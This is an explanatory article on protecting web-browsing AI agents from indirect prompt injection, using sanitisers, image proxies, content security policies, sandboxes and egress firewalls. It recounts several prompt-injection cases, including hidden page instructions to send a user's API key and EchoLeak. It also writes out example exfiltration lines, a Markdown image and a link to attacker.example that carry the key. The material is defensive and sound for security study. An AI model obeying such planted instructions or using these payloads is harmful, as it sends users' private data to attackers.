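# Sandboxing, network isolation and content security policies for AI agents that browse and display web content

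## How web content can turn an AI agent against its user

An AI agent is a language model connected to tools, so its text output triggers actions such as fetching a web page, sending an email, running a program or clicking a button. Some agents run inside chat assistants or on a programmer's machine. Others are part of an agentic browser, such as OpenAI's ChatGPT Atlas or Perplexity's Comet, which has a built-in agent that can read the user's pages and often act on them. In Atlas's agent mode, the agent views pages, clicks and types inside the browser much as the user would, according to OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025).

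AI agents that browse the web read a good deal of text written by strangers. Anyone can publish a web page or send an email containing instructions meant for whatever AI system reads it. An agent that follows those instructions may send private data to the person who wrote them, click something it should not, or run hostile code. Sandboxing, network restrictions, content security policies and output sanitising can limit the damage, and none of them depends on the model resisting the instructions.

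An attacker can publish an ordinary article containing a hidden instruction to send the user's data to an address the attacker controls. When a user asks an agent to summarize the page, the agent can return a good summary and also send the data. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) describes a laboratory version of this attack, with the user's message fixed as "summarize this page". One of the hidden instructions was in the page's description tag, which browsers do not display. It was worded as a security requirement and told the agent to verify connectivity before replying by making a web request that included the user's API key (a password that programs use).

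### The agent loop

Agents work in a loop. InfoQ's *OpenAI Begins Article Series on Codex CLI Internals* (2026) explains that the software takes input from a user, and a model generates either a reply or a tool call. Lan and colleagues describe a more detailed version called ReAct (for "reasoning and acting"), in which the model writes some intermediate reasoning, emits a tool call in a fixed format and pauses. Ordinary software then parses the call, runs the tool and adds the result to the model's input. The model reads the longer input and repeats the process until it produces a reply.

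So the model itself only ever writes text. Everything with a consequence happens in the conventional software around it, which is why conventional security measures have something to hold on to. In the example the loop runs like this:

1. The user asks for a summary of the page.
2. The agent fetches the page, and the page's text joins the text the model reads.
3. The model follows the hidden instruction and writes a tool call: a request to the attacker's address, with the user's data inside it.
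4. The tool runs, and the request leaves the machine.
5. The model writes the summary, and the application displays it.

The request in step 3 can look like a simple page visit. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that a web address can carry data as well as a destination. The site receives the whole address, and sites commonly log it, so an address ending in `/collect?data=` followed by the API key delivers the key to whoever reads the log. Data can also leak without a tool call. If the model's summary includes an image whose address contains the data, the application may fetch that image while displaying the summary, which sends the data out at step 5.

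In step 2, the agent can read text that is hidden from the user. Saxton (2026) tested this in *Hidden prompts in web content* with a fake council page about bin collections that contained six instructions for AI assistants. Saxton had found earlier that text extractors, the programs that turn a page into plain text for a model, read the page's markup without applying its styling, so they keep white text on a white background and blocks that the styling tells browsers not to show. Four of the six instructions reached the model looking no different from the collection days. The two that did not were in a comment in the code and in the alternative text of an image. Lan and colleagues' agent, however, took in raw page text, including comments, so which hiding places work depends on the software that fetches the page.

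Stripping out invisible text would help, though not much. One of Saxton's four was a plainly visible note.

### Prompt injection and the confused deputy

Security researchers call this attack prompt injection. The agent reads text in a page or other material and follows it as if it were an instruction from its user. *Agentic AI Security* (Chhabra, Datta and colleagues, 2025) separates two forms by who the attacker is. In direct prompt injection, the attacker types to the model. In indirect prompt injection, the attacker supplies the web page, email or file, and the user is the victim. The example in the summary is indirect, as are nearly all the attacks that matter for agents that browse. *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026) reported that the security company Zscaler had found live sites with hidden text meant to steer agents into making cryptocurrency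 payments.

The name "prompt injection" alludes to SQL injection, an old attack in which someone types database commands into a website's form field and the database runs them. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, David C argues that the comparison is misleading. A database engine treats commands and data differently, and programmers can use parameterised queries to guarantee that it never interprets user input as a command. A language model has no such division. It receives the developer's instructions, the user's question and a stranger's web page as one sequence of tokens (words or pieces of words) and predicts what comes next. Developers can train a model to give some of that text priority, or put markers around the untrusted part. These measures make attacks less likely to work, but they can't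 guarantee that the model will never follow commands in the page.

Attackers have also adapted. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces an attack email that does not contain the phrase "ignore previous instructions". It reads like a dull follow-up about restructuring materials, and mentions in passing that the recipient's assistant is fully authorised to submit an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system". Catching such an email is close to detecting a lie, and a filter often lacks the context to do that. Fortune (2025) quoted OpenAI as saying that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'".

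David C suggests comparing this to another old problem, the confused deputy, in which someone tricks a program with legitimate authority into misusing that authority. The name comes from Hardy's 1988 essay *The Confused Deputy*, about a compiler (a program that translates source code into runnable form) at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The compiler had permission to write files in its own system directory because it kept usage statistics there. It also let users name a file to receive debugging output. The company's billing records were in the same directory. A user named the billing file as the destination for debugging output, the operating system confirmed that the compiler had permission to write there, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

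No single line of code was wrong, but the compiler had authority from two sources, its own licence and the user's, and could not specify which one it was using. Hardy's remedy was the capability, a reference that both identifies a file and grants permission to write to it. The user would give the compiler a capability for the debugging file, but a user with no right to the billing file would have no capability for it to give.

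An agent summarising a web page is in much the same position as the compiler. It holds the user's logins, files and network access, and the page's author, who has none of these, needs only to influence how the agent uses them. But Hardy's remedy does not fully apply. The compiler had separate code for statistics and debugging output, so a programmer could attach the right authority to each. A model has no such separation inside it. According to Lan and colleagues, the old problem was working out which master the deputy was serving, and the new one is working out what the master meant. David C calls language models "inherently confusable" for this reason, and concludes that designers should reduce the likelihood and impact of attacks because they cannot expect to eliminate them.

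### Three harms

Data exfiltration means sending private data to someone who should not have it, as in the summary example. The best-known real case is EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft Copilot from mid-2025. Chhabra and colleagues describe how emails containing crafted instructions could make Copilot send out sensitive data in a zero-click attack, which requires no action by the user.

Clickjacking means disguising or covering part of a page so that a click has an effect the clicker did not intend. The developer site web.dev describes the textbook case, in which an attacker displays a genuine site in an iframe (a web page displayed inside another) and lays transparent buttons over it. Visitors think they are using the genuine site, but their clicks go where the attacker chose. An agent that clicks on the user's behalf could make the same mistake if, for example, a harmless "continue reading"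 button on an article sat over something else. This can happen without prompt injection, even when the agent follows its user's instructions exactly.

The third harm is remote code execution, in which an outsider runs a program of their choice on someone else's machine. Many agents routinely write and run code, so anyone who can influence the text an agent reads can also influence the code it runs. Chhabra and colleagues cite CVE-2024-5565, a flaw in which AI-generated code made arbitrary code execution possible. If the agent in the example had a command line, the hidden instruction could just as easily have been to download and run a file.

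### Origins and the same-origin policy

Browsers have had to cope with hostile pages for decades, and their main rule for keeping sites apart rests on the idea of an origin. An origin is the scheme, host name and port of a web address. The scheme is the `http` or `https` at the front, and the port is a number, usually left out, that identifies a service on the host. Barth (2011), in *The Web Origin Concept*, the document that standardised the idea, gives lists of addresses from which these comparisons with `http://example.com/` come:

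| Address | Same origin? | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `http://example.com/path/file` | Yes | The path does not count |
| `http://example.com:80/` | Yes | 80 is the usual port for `http` |
| `http://example.com:8080/` | No | Different port |
| `https://example.com/` | No | Different scheme |
| `http://www.example.com/` | No | Different host |
| `http://example.org/` | No | Different host |

The first row implies that if a university hosts every student's pages under one host name, the pages all share an origin, so the browser's same-origin policy does not protect them from each other.

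Under the same-origin policy, a script from one origin may not read another origin's data. WHATWG's *Loading web pages*, part of the current HTML standard, gives the example of a bank's page that tries to inspect a charity's page and gets a security error. The same rule keeps an attacker's page in one tab from reading a bank's page in another.

The same-origin policy restricts reading far more than sending. A page may display images from any origin and submit forms to any origin. W3C's *Same Origin Policy* explains that a ban on sending across origins would also ban links between sites, and then there would be no web. It adds that this freedom to send makes clickjacking possible. The freedom also makes data exfiltration easier, because once an attacker has obtained private data inside the browser, the policy does little to stop them from sending it out.

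The same-origin policy usually stops an attacker's script from reading another site's content, but an AI agent can get around that restriction. Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, describe a version of the summary attack in which the attacker's page embeds the user's bank in an iframe, next to a form that submits itself. A hidden instruction tells the agent to include the iframe in its summary and type that summary into the form. The agent reads the bank's page with the user's own access, so no script has to read across origins. The attack works only if the bank allows other sites to frame it and has permissive cookie settings, which is a real limitation. Still, where an agent can read across origins, the separation between sites is only as strong as the agent's resistance to prompt injection.

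### Four defences

*Sandboxing* means running the agent's tools in an environment that limits which files, system functions and network addresses they can reach. It acts at step 4, when the tool runs. A command from the hidden instruction may start, but it can't reach the user's other files.

*Network restriction* controls egress, the traffic leaving a machine or network, often by blocking all destinations not on an allowlist. It acts at the end of step 4, before the request to the attacker's address leaves.

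*Sanitising* means using code to remove or neutralise dangerous elements in the agent's answer before displaying it. This happens at the start of step 5 and can delete the image whose address contains the user's data.

A *content security policy* (CSP) is a list, sent with a web page, of the sources the page may load from or connect to and the sites that may frame it. The browser applies it at the end of step 5. Even if the image got past the sanitiser, the browser will not fetch it from a server missing from the list.

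The sandbox is also the main barrier to remote code execution, and a CSP's framing rules protect a site against classic clickjacking.

All four defences apply after the model has been fooled. OpenAI compares this to customer service, where a company expects some customers to mislead its staff and so has a separate system limit the refunds a customer can receive. In OpenAI's terms, an attacker needs a source (a way to influence the agent) and a sink (an action that is dangerous in the wrong context), and the four defences work on sinks. Training still matters a great deal. OpenAI reports that most attacks it knows of against ChatGPT fail because the model refuses.

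The four controls have obvious gaps even in theory. Lan and colleagues note that a sandbox does little when the agent is supposed to make web requests, and that an attacker can get around an allowlist by routing data through a trusted site that redirects visitors elsewhere. Some harm would not be blocked by any of the four. One of Saxton's instructions was for the assistant to report that a £52 bin subscription was free, and a false sentence in a summary breaks no network rule and contains no dangerous markup.

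Several kinds of evidence show how well the defences work. Specifications and technical documentation come first, covering the display of output and then the running of agents. They establish what a correctly configured defence guarantees. Controlled experiments on data theft follow, then tests of whether agentic browsers keep websites apart and experiments on clickjacking. These measure what happens with particular models, products and attacks. Disclosed failures come last: leaks through displayed output, leaks past allowlists, and code that ran outside its sandbox. They prove that gaps existed in real products but provide little evidence of how common such gaps are.

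## What the browser enforces when an agent's output is displayed

Chat clients usually ask the model for Markdown, a plain-text notation in which asterisks mark bold text and `![caption](address)` marks an image. The client converts that text into part of a web page, and the browser fetches whatever the page needs. If the hidden instruction in the summary example tells the model to leak the user's API key through an image, the leak goes like this:

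1. The model ends its summary with `![chart](https://attacker.example/log?d=KEY)`, where `KEY` stands for the user's API key.
2. A Markdown parser converts the answer to HTML, the markup language of web pages. The last line becomes `<img src="https://attacker.example/log?d=KEY" alt="chart">`.
3. A sanitiser, if the client has one, removes dangerous elements. An image is an ordinary element, so it may well stay.
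4. The browser parses the HTML into a tree of elements (the document) and finds an image in it.
5. The browser requests the image, and the attacker's server logs the address with the key inside.

The attack needs no click, because a browser fetches images automatically to draw the page, whereas it normally follows a link only when someone clicks it. The image doesn't have to exist. Chi's *Data exfiltration via Markdown image tags* describes an instruction that asks the model to end its reply with a loading indicator. The attacker's server returns an error and the user sees a broken-image icon for half a second at most, but by then the key is in the server's log.

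The client's developer can break this chain by sanitising the HTML, sending image requests through a proxy, or giving the browser a content security policy.

### Sanitising the answer

A crude sanitiser searches the text for dangerous patterns and deletes them, which is easy to get around. Deleting `<script>` from `<scr<script>ipt>` leaves `<script>`. HTML can also run a script without a script tag. For example, `<img src="x" onerror="...">` runs the code in `onerror` when the image fails to load.

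A deeper problem is that the filter checks the output as text, but the browser parses it as HTML, under rules that tolerate many mistakes. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the CSP standard, gives an example in which the attacker supplies only the beginning of a script tag. A filter that looks for complete script elements misses it. When the browser parses the whole page, the unfinished tag runs on into the next legitimate script tag, and the two become one script element that loads the attacker's file.

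With an allowlist, the developer instead lists the elements and attributes an answer may contain, such as paragraphs, tables, code blocks and links to `https` addresses. The sanitiser removes everything else, including dangerous elements the developer has never heard of.

The sanitiser should apply this list to the parsed document, because the HTML parser has already turned sloppy markup into definite elements. It should also run after the Markdown parser, because the image in the example contains no HTML before that step. Ideally the client then passes the cleaned tree straight to the browser. If it writes the tree out as text and parses it again, or lets a code highlighter edit it afterwards, the browser may receive elements that the sanitiser never checked.

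It is still unclear how to handle the image, because a malicious `img` element with an `https` address differs from a legitimate illustration only in its address. Removing all remote images is the safest rule, and a client that can do without them should probably adopt it.

### Image proxies

Clients that need to show images can use an image proxy, a server the developer controls that fetches images on the browser's behalf. In Chi's design, the client sends every image request to the proxy. The proxy removes the query string (the part of the address after the `?`), fetches only from a short list of domains and refuses redirects, so the attacker's server never receives a request.

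The list of domains provides most of the protection. Without it, the proxy itself would send the key to `attacker.example`. Removing query strings would not be enough to prevent this, because the key can also be in the path, as in `https://attacker.example/KEY.png`, or in the host name, as in `https://KEY.attacker.example/`.

Chi harshly criticizes the alternatives, which include telling the model not to write such images, asking it whether an image looks safe, and refusing addresses with long query strings. Chi objects that a model under attack can't be trusted to judge whether the attack succeeded. That is right about the first two, but ordinary code can enforce a length limit without using the model. A length limit still fails because an attacker can put the key in the path or spread it over several short addresses.

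### A policy for an imaginary chat client

A CSP is useful when the earlier measures miss something. W3C describes it as defence in depth and "not intended as a first line of defense" against injected content. Suppose the chat client's address is `https://chat.example`. Its server could send this policy in a header along with the page (on a single line in practice):

```
Content-Security-Policy:
  default-src 'none';
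  script-src 'nonce-q7Vd0mXzR2cLw9TgKf4YuA';
  style-src 'self';
  font-src 'self';
  img-src 'self' https://files.example/chat/;
  connect-src 'self';
  frame-src https://panels.example;
  form-action 'self';
  base-uri 'none';
  frame-ancestors 'none'
```

Each line is a directive, and `'self'` means the page's own origin. Most directives cover one kind of request. For example, when the page needs an image, the browser checks the image's address against the `img-src` list before sending the request, and again for each redirect.

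- `default-src 'none'` is the fallback for kinds of request that have no directive of their own, such as video. An explicit directive replaces the fallback completely, so `img-src` here takes nothing from `default-src`. W3C suggests starting from `'none'` and adding only what the page needs.
- `script-src` contains a nonce, a random value that the server generates afresh every time it sends the policy. The server puts the same value in its own script tags, and the browser runs only scripts that carry it. W3C recommends at least 128 bits, because anyone who can guess the nonce can run any script.
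- `style-src` and `font-src` limit style sheets and fonts to the client's own.
- `img-src` permits images from the client's origin and from one directory on `files.example`, a shared file host.
- `connect-src` covers connections that scripts open. It also covers the `ping` attribute, which makes a link notify another address when someone clicks it.
- `frame-src` lists the pages that may appear in iframes inside the client.
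- `form-action` lists the addresses to which forms may send their contents.
- `base-uri` closes a hole that nonces open. HTML's `base` element changes how the browser completes short addresses. If an attacker could insert `<base href="https://attacker.example">`, the client's own tag for `/app.js` would load the attacker's `/app.js` instead, with a valid nonce.
- `frame-ancestors` works in the opposite direction from `frame-src`: it lists the sites that may display the client in an iframe. The browser checks the page that contains the client, then the page that contains that one, and so on to the top, and every one of them must be on the list. This is the standard protection against classic clickjacking, though it does less when an agent is doing the clicking.

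A developer can put most of these directives in a `meta` element inside the page instead of the response header, but the browser then ignores `frame-ancestors` and doesn't apply the policy to anything before that element. A report-only version of the header, meant for testing a policy, blocks nothing.

### Four outputs under this policy

Assume the sanitiser has failed completely and the client has no image proxy, so the policy is on its own.

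The browser classes the request to `attacker.example` as an image request, finds no match in `img-src`, and blocks it before it leaves the machine. This stops the attack even if nobody recognises it as one. If the policy had a `report-to` directive, the browser would also send the developer a report of the violation. Under W3C's rules, that report keeps the query string, so the developer's logs would contain the user's key. That is much better than the attacker having the key, but it is a reason to treat the logs as sensitive.

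An injected script tag without the nonce doesn't run, whether its code is in the page or on another server. The `onerror` trick also fails, because nonces apply only to whole script and style elements, not to attributes. This protection would disappear if the developer replaced the nonce with `'unsafe-inline'`, a keyword that permits scripts written directly into the page. Browsers ignore the keyword if a nonce is in the same list. W3C advises against using `'unsafe-inline'`, but developers may be tempted to use it when older code stops working.

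An image at an allowed host that forwards requests is a harder case, because forwarding can mean two things. One is redirecting the browser to another address, as pages on many sites do. Suppose `https://chat.example/go?to=` is such a page, and the model writes an image whose address ends with the attacker's address and the key. The browser sends the first request because `chat.example` is on the list. The server replies with a redirect to `attacker.example`, which the browser doesn't follow because that address isn't on the list. The key reaches only the client's own server.

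The browser checks the original request's path against the policy, but after a redirect it compares only the scheme, host and port. The policy permits only the `/chat/` directory on `files.example`, so a direct request for `https://files.example/mallory/log?d=KEY` fails. The same request succeeds if it is redirected from `chat.example/go`. An attacker with an account on the file host and access to its logs could then read the key. W3C made this compromise deliberately, because a hostile page could otherwise try one policy after another to discover where another site was redirecting its visitors.

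The other kind of forwarding happens on a server. A link-preview service, for instance, might take an address, fetch it and return the result. The browser makes one request to an allowed host and gets no redirect to check, so the policy can't block the server's request. EchoLeak got data out of Microsoft Copilot partly through such a service. An image proxy also fetches addresses this way, so it needs its own list of domains.

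The last output is a link, say `[Read the full notes](https://attacker.example/notes?d=KEY)`. If the user clicks it, the browser opens the attacker's site and sends it the key in the URL. The policy doesn't prevent this. The specification defines a check that runs before the browser moves to a new page, but only the `form-action` directive uses it, and that directive restricts only form submissions. An earlier CSP proposal included a `navigate-to` directive for links, but the current draft has no equivalent.

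Restricting which sites links can lead to would be hard in a chat client, since people expect an assistant to link to pages all over the web. A client can show the full URL and ask the user to confirm before opening it, which helps if the user reads the URL.

Navigation doesn't always require a click, either. HTML's `meta` element can tell the browser to go to another page after a given number of seconds, which can be zero. CSP treats this like any other navigation, so an answer containing that element could send the whole tab, and the key, to the attacker. An allowlist sanitiser would have removed the element, which is a good reason to use both a sanitiser and CSP.

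### Pages and panels with scripts of their own

Some answers are meant to include scripts, such as an interactive chart built by an agent or a booking form supplied by a tool. The nonce rule blocks these scripts. Giving them the nonce would be unsafe, because a script running in the chat page's origin can read the conversation and act as the user.

The usual solution is an iframe with a `sandbox` attribute. According to WHATWG's *The iframe element*, part of the HTML standard, the browser then gives the page inside an origin that matches no other, disables its scripts and forms, and stops its links from opening in other frames or windows. The developer can restore individual abilities with keywords. With `sandbox="allow-scripts"`, a chart can run its code, but the same-origin policy keeps it from reading the chat around it.

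Combining `allow-scripts` with `allow-same-origin` is dangerous when the page comes from the same origin as the client. `allow-same-origin` gives the page its real origin back, so its script can remove the `sandbox` attribute, reload the page and escape. WHATWG also advises serving hostile files from a separate domain, because the attribute restricts a page only while it is inside the iframe, and an attacker might persuade the user to open the file's address directly.

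The sandbox attribute doesn't restrict ordinary network requests. A sandboxed chart that contains private sales figures can still send them out in the URL of an image request, so it needs a CSP too. If the client writes the page into the iframe with the `srcdoc` attribute, the browser applies the client's own CSP to the new page. W3C included that rule because otherwise any page could escape its policy by creating a frame. The copied policy includes the nonce rule, which blocks the chart's scripts. A client that wants those scripts to run needs to load the chart from another origin with its own policy.

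That is roughly how chat clients display panels from tool servers. Model Context Protocol (2025), the project behind an open standard (MCP) for connecting AI applications to tools, announced a proposed extension for interactive panels, MCP Apps, which maintainers at OpenAI and Anthropic wrote with the creators of an earlier project. The detailed rules are in the specification by Salomon, Yosef and colleagues (2025), in *SEP-1865*, which reached stable status in January 2026. For a client that runs in a browser, they work as follows:

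1. The tool server supplies the panel as HTML, with a list of the domains it needs to contact.
2. The client opens an iframe containing a proxy page, which must have a different origin from the client.
3. The proxy page loads the panel in a second iframe inside the first, under a CSP that matches the server's list.
4. The panel and the client communicate only by passing messages through the proxy page, and the client can refuse any of them.

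The client may tighten the policy but must not permit a domain that the server didn't declare. If the server declares none, the panel can't connect to any outside server. The default policy includes `'unsafe-inline'`, which makes sense here despite W3C's advice against it. The whole panel is untrusted, so there are no trusted scripts to mark with a nonce, and the policy only has to limit where the panel can connect.

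The rules also require the outer iframe to have both `allow-scripts` and `allow-same-origin`. WHATWG warns about this combination, but it is safe for the client here because the iframe must have a different origin from the client. If a client lets the panel and the proxy page share an origin, a script in the panel can access the proxy page, so the proxy page should have a policy at least as strict as the panel's.

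Panels should also be kept apart from each other. According to Model Context Protocol's *CSP & CORS*, a server can request a fixed address for its panels. In Claude, that address begins with 32 characters derived from the server's address, so each server gets a different origin. For servers that don't request one, Salomon and colleagues' default is typically one origin per conversation. Panels from two servers in the same conversation might then share an origin, in which case the same-origin policy would not separate them.

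If a panel is not itself malicious but loads a compromised library or displays text that a stranger wrote, the policy keeps its data away from undeclared domains. The policy offers much less protection against a malicious tool server, because the server writes the list of domains and can include `attacker.example`. Salomon and colleagues say that clients should warn users about panels that need outside domains, and may keep lists of their own, but neither is compulsory. A malicious server may not need to declare a domain at all. Panels can call the server's tools through the client, so any data in the panel can go back to the server in a tool call, which CSP does not restrict. A client that shows a panel something private has to assume that the server can read it.

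### Routes that the policy does not cover

Setting `default-src 'none'` doesn't restrict everything, because several directives don't fall back to it. CentralCSP, a vendor of CSP tools, lists `form-action`, `base-uri`, `frame-ancestors` and `sandbox` among them, which matches the fallback rules in W3C's text. A page with only `default-src 'none'` can therefore still submit a form to any address, and any site can display it in an iframe. Salomon and colleagues' sample policy for panels has no `form-action`. This omission matters if the client adds `allow-forms` to the iframe sandbox, which otherwise disables forms.

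A policy without `default-src` lets the browser send prefetch requests to any server. Browsers can prefetch pages and files that they expect to need soon, and these requests have no directive of their own. If the policy includes `default-src`, a prefetch may go only to servers that some directive in the policy allows. W3C gives the example of a policy that only bans images, scripts and fonts, and so still lets data out through prefetching. It also points out that a policy prevents leaks only as well as its most permissive source list does. For example, `default-src 'none'; img-src *` allows an image request to carry data to any server.

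DNS prefetching is a separate feature that looks up a host's numerical address before the browser connects to it. The lookup alone can leak data. If a page makes the browser look up `KEY.attacker.example`, the query carries `KEY` to the name server for `attacker.example`, which the attacker can run. CSP's checks on web requests don't apply because the browser makes no web request. The page needs only a `link` element to trigger the lookup. An allowlist sanitiser would remove that element from an ordinary answer, but a panel with its own scripts can add it.

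`connect-src` has no effect on WebRTC, the browser feature for video calls and direct connections between machines, because WebRTC doesn't use the browser's normal system for making requests. W3C's draft includes a `webrtc 'block'` directive that would disable it, but CentralCSP reports that no browser had shipped the directive as of mid-2026. In the discussion at Mozilla's *Implement CSP 'webrtc' directive*, a developer from the file-storage project Peergos asks for it so that untrusted apps can run on private data without being able to steal the data. A chat client faces the same risk when it runs untrusted code in a panel. The gap matters less for the main chat page, because an attacker has to get a script running there before they can use WebRTC.

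A page's content security policy (CSP) doesn't restrict the agent. When a tool makes a web request from a server or a command line, no browser applies a CSP. W3C says that policies shouldn't interfere with browser extensions, and Chrome exempts them, so an agent that runs as an extension can make requests that the page could not.

A newer proposal would close most of the gaps in the browser. In *Connection Allowlists*, West, who works at Google and is an editor of the CSP specification, argues that CSP's division of requests into types is the wrong approach to data theft, since a leak through a font request is as bad as a leak through an image. The proposed header contains a single list of allowed addresses that applies to every kind of connection, including WebRTC and DNS prefetching, and in the current draft any redirected request fails. Chrome for Developers' *Connection Allowlists origin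 trial* adds that the list covers navigation, so it should also stop the link in the fourth output. Blocking links this way would be a nuisance in the main chat window but suits a panel well.

Report URI's *Connection Allowlist* says the feature shipped in Chrome 152 and calls it a browser standard, but West's draft states that it is neither a W3C standard nor on the way to becoming one. Toreini, commenting in a W3C design review in February 2026, liked the goal but noted that no other stakeholders had taken a position. The draft is also unfinished in places, and under its WebRTC heading West writes, "I have no idea how any of this works from a spec perspective".

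Even a finished version would apply to one page at a time. If a script can reach another page of the same origin that has a looser list or none, it can send its data from there. West's remedy is to sandbox the restricted page so that it shares an origin with nothing else. The list also doesn't cover messages between frames, so a panel could still pass data to the client and request a tool call.

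## What sandboxes and network rules enforce when an agent runs

When an agent runs a command, the operating system and the network have to limit what the command can do. Suppose the hidden instruction in the article tells the agent to download and run a script that finds the user's SSH keys, which are files used to log in to other machines, and posts them to `attacker.example`. A sandbox can stop the script from reading the keys, and a network rule can stop it from connecting to the attacker's server.

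Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, which announced a sandbox for its programming agent Claude Code in October 2025, explains why an agent needs both network and file isolation. Without network isolation, a hijacked agent can send out any file it can read. Without file isolation, it can escape the sandbox and regain network access, for example by editing a start-up file that runs outside the sandbox.

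### What a sandboxed program shares with its host

A program can't open a file or a network connection by itself. It makes a system call to the kernel, the core of the operating system, which does the work. Linux has about 400 system calls, and Kerrisk (2023), in *Using seccomp to limit the kernel attack surface*, points out that each one is a possible way to attack the kernel. Whoever takes over the kernel controls the machine and every sandbox on it, so the main difference between sandboxes is how much of the host's kernel the untrusted program can reach. From weakest to strongest, the usual types are:

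| Sandbox | What it shares with the host | What a flaw in the shared part exposes |
|---|---|---|
| Operating-system rules | The kernel, apart from whatever the rules forbid | The whole machine |
| Container | The same | The whole machine, including its other containers |
| User-space kernel (gVisor) | A small set of kernel calls | The whole machine, but only after a second flaw, in gVisor itself |
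| Small virtual machine (Firecracker) | The processor's virtualisation features and the software that manages them | The whole machine, including its other virtual machines |

Operating-system rules are restrictions that the host's own kernel applies to a process. Sandbox developers on Linux usually combine several mechanisms:

- Namespaces give a process its own view of a resource, such as the list of running processes or the network interfaces. A process in an empty network namespace has no network card to send through.
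- Seccomp filters system calls. It can check a call's arguments but can't follow a pointer to text elsewhere in memory, so it can forbid opening files but can't tell one file name from another. The Linux kernel documentation's *Seccomp BPF (SECure COMPuting with filters)* warns that "System call filtering isn't a sandbox" and describes it as a tool for people who build sandboxes.
- Landlock lets a process restrict itself to particular directories. Every process it starts inherits the restriction, and none of them can remove it, according to Salaün (2026), in *Landlock*. The network rules are cruder. They name ports and not destinations, so a rule that permits port 443 permits nearly every website.

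On macOS, Seatbelt does a similar job. Claude Code's sandbox uses Seatbelt there and bubblewrap, a small program that sets up namespaces, on Linux.

Kernel rules have a big advantage over checks inside the agent's own software because they also apply to the processes a command starts. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* explains that the software can inspect a command before running it but can't monitor what that command starts. An agent blocked from running the download tool `curl` can write a few lines of Python to download the same file, but the kernel's rules still apply to the Python process.

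Permitted system calls still go to the host's kernel, so the rules don't protect against kernel bugs that those calls can trigger. gVisor's *Security Model* gives the example of Dirty Cow, a Linux bug that a program could trigger by opening a particular file and running several threads at once. If the timing worked, the program gained control of a page of the system's memory.

A container packages a program with the files and libraries it needs, and runs it under these same kernel mechanisms. It can hide the user's files completely, but it shares the host's kernel. *Firecracker* (Agache, Brooker and colleagues, 2020) calls seccomp the most important security boundary of a Linux container, but notes that blocking more system calls to protect the kernel also breaks programs. A trivial Linux program needs 15 different system calls, while a typical Ubuntu installation needs 224. Choosing which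 calls to allow is harder for an agent, because nobody knows in advance what software it will write or install.

gVisor, an open-source project, avoids this trade-off by putting a second kernel in between. Its developers rewrote the Linux system calls from scratch in Go, a language that rules out many memory bugs, and the result runs as an ordinary program. When sandboxed code requests its process number, gVisor looks it up in a table of its own, and the host's kernel never receives the call. For other requests gVisor has to make host calls itself, under a strict seccomp filter. An attacker would therefore have to break gVisor and then Linux, which share no code. The price is that sandboxed programs can't use any kernel feature that gVisor lacks, and those that make many system calls run more slowly.

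A microVM is a small virtual machine with its own complete Linux kernel, which the processor's hardware separates from the host. Compromising that kernel gives an attacker control of only the virtual machine. The host is still exposed through the software that runs the machine and supplies its virtual disk and network card. Agache and colleagues wrote Firecracker for Amazon to keep that software small. It has about 50,000 lines of code, compared with more than 1.4 million in QEMU, the general-purpose program it replaced. Firecracker also depends on KVM, a part of the Linux kernel with another 120,000 lines.

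The order of the last two types is debatable. NVIDIA prefers full virtualisation and warns that gVisor's guarantees may be weaker. gVisor's developers reply that a virtual machine is only as safe as the device software it exposes, and that virtualisation hardware doesn't make a system secure by itself. Neither type stops side-channel attacks such as Spectre, in which a program infers secrets from the behaviour of a processor it shares.

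For most agents, this argument matters less than the quality of everything around the sandbox. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (May 2026) reports that gVisor, seccomp and virtual machines had all been dependable, and that the component that failed was an allowlist proxy the company had written itself. Sandboxes also tend to cover only part of an agent. According to Anthropic's documentation, Claude Code's sandbox for shell commands doesn't cover its built-in file tools, tool servers or hooks (commands that run automatically on certain events). To restrict those as well, a user can run the whole program inside a sandbox such as a container or virtual machine.

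### One request, four steps

In *A sandbox without a network boundary is only half a sandbox*, an article for the hosting company Vercel, Tuttle (2026) writes, "Isolation without egress control contains the process, not its consequences." A script that can read a secret and reach the internet can send the secret out without escaping its virtual machine.

The usual remedy is default-deny egress, in which a firewall enforces an allowlist. When the script requests `https://attacker.example/collect?data=KEY`, the firewall has four chances to step in:

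1. *Name lookup.* The script sends the host name to a DNS resolver, a server that finds the matching IP address. The firewall can refuse to look up names that are not on the allowlist.
2. *Connection.* The script opens a connection to that IP address, normally on port 443. The firewall can check the address and port.
3. *TLS handshake.* The script and the server set up encryption. The script's first message normally contains the server's name in plain text, in a field called Server Name Indication (SNI), so the firewall can check the name again.
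4. *Request.* The script sends the path, the headers and any data, all encrypted. The firewall can check these only if it can decrypt them.

Products differ mainly in how far down this list they go.

| Filter | What it can read | What can get past it |
|---|---|---|
| By IP address | Address and port | Requests to other sites at a permitted address |
| By server name | Host name | Data in the path or body, and requests for a different site inside the encryption |
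| Decrypting proxy | The whole request | Data sent through functions that the policy permits |

Filtering by IP address works for any kind of traffic, so it is useful for private networks and old protocols. It works poorly for websites, because thousands of sites can share one address and a large service's addresses keep changing. According to *Sandbox firewall*, Vercel's documentation for its own product, a Vercel policy that lists only address ranges leaves DNS unrestricted, even if all the ranges are private, so code in the sandbox can still send data out in DNS lookups.

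By default, Vercel's firewall filters only by the server name in the TLS handshake. A script can get around this with domain fronting, which puts a permitted name in the handshake and a different one in the encrypted `Host` header. If both sites use the same content delivery network, and the network allows the mismatch, the request goes to the second site. Many networks reject such requests, but Vercel's firewall doesn't by default. The company suggests permitting only narrow, single-purpose host names. Plain `http` traffic has no TLS handshake, so Vercel can filter it only by IP address.

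A decrypting proxy reads encrypted requests by posing as the destination server. The operator installs a certificate authority in the sandbox so that programs there accept the proxy's certificates. The proxy decrypts each request, checks it and opens a second encrypted connection to the real server. The operator can therefore set precise rules, such as allowing uploads to one path and blocking everything else on that site. However, programs with their own lists of trusted authorities need extra configuration, and the proxy handles every secret unencrypted. Vercel and Cloudflare both create a separate authority for each sandbox, so one sandbox's authority can't be used to read another's traffic.

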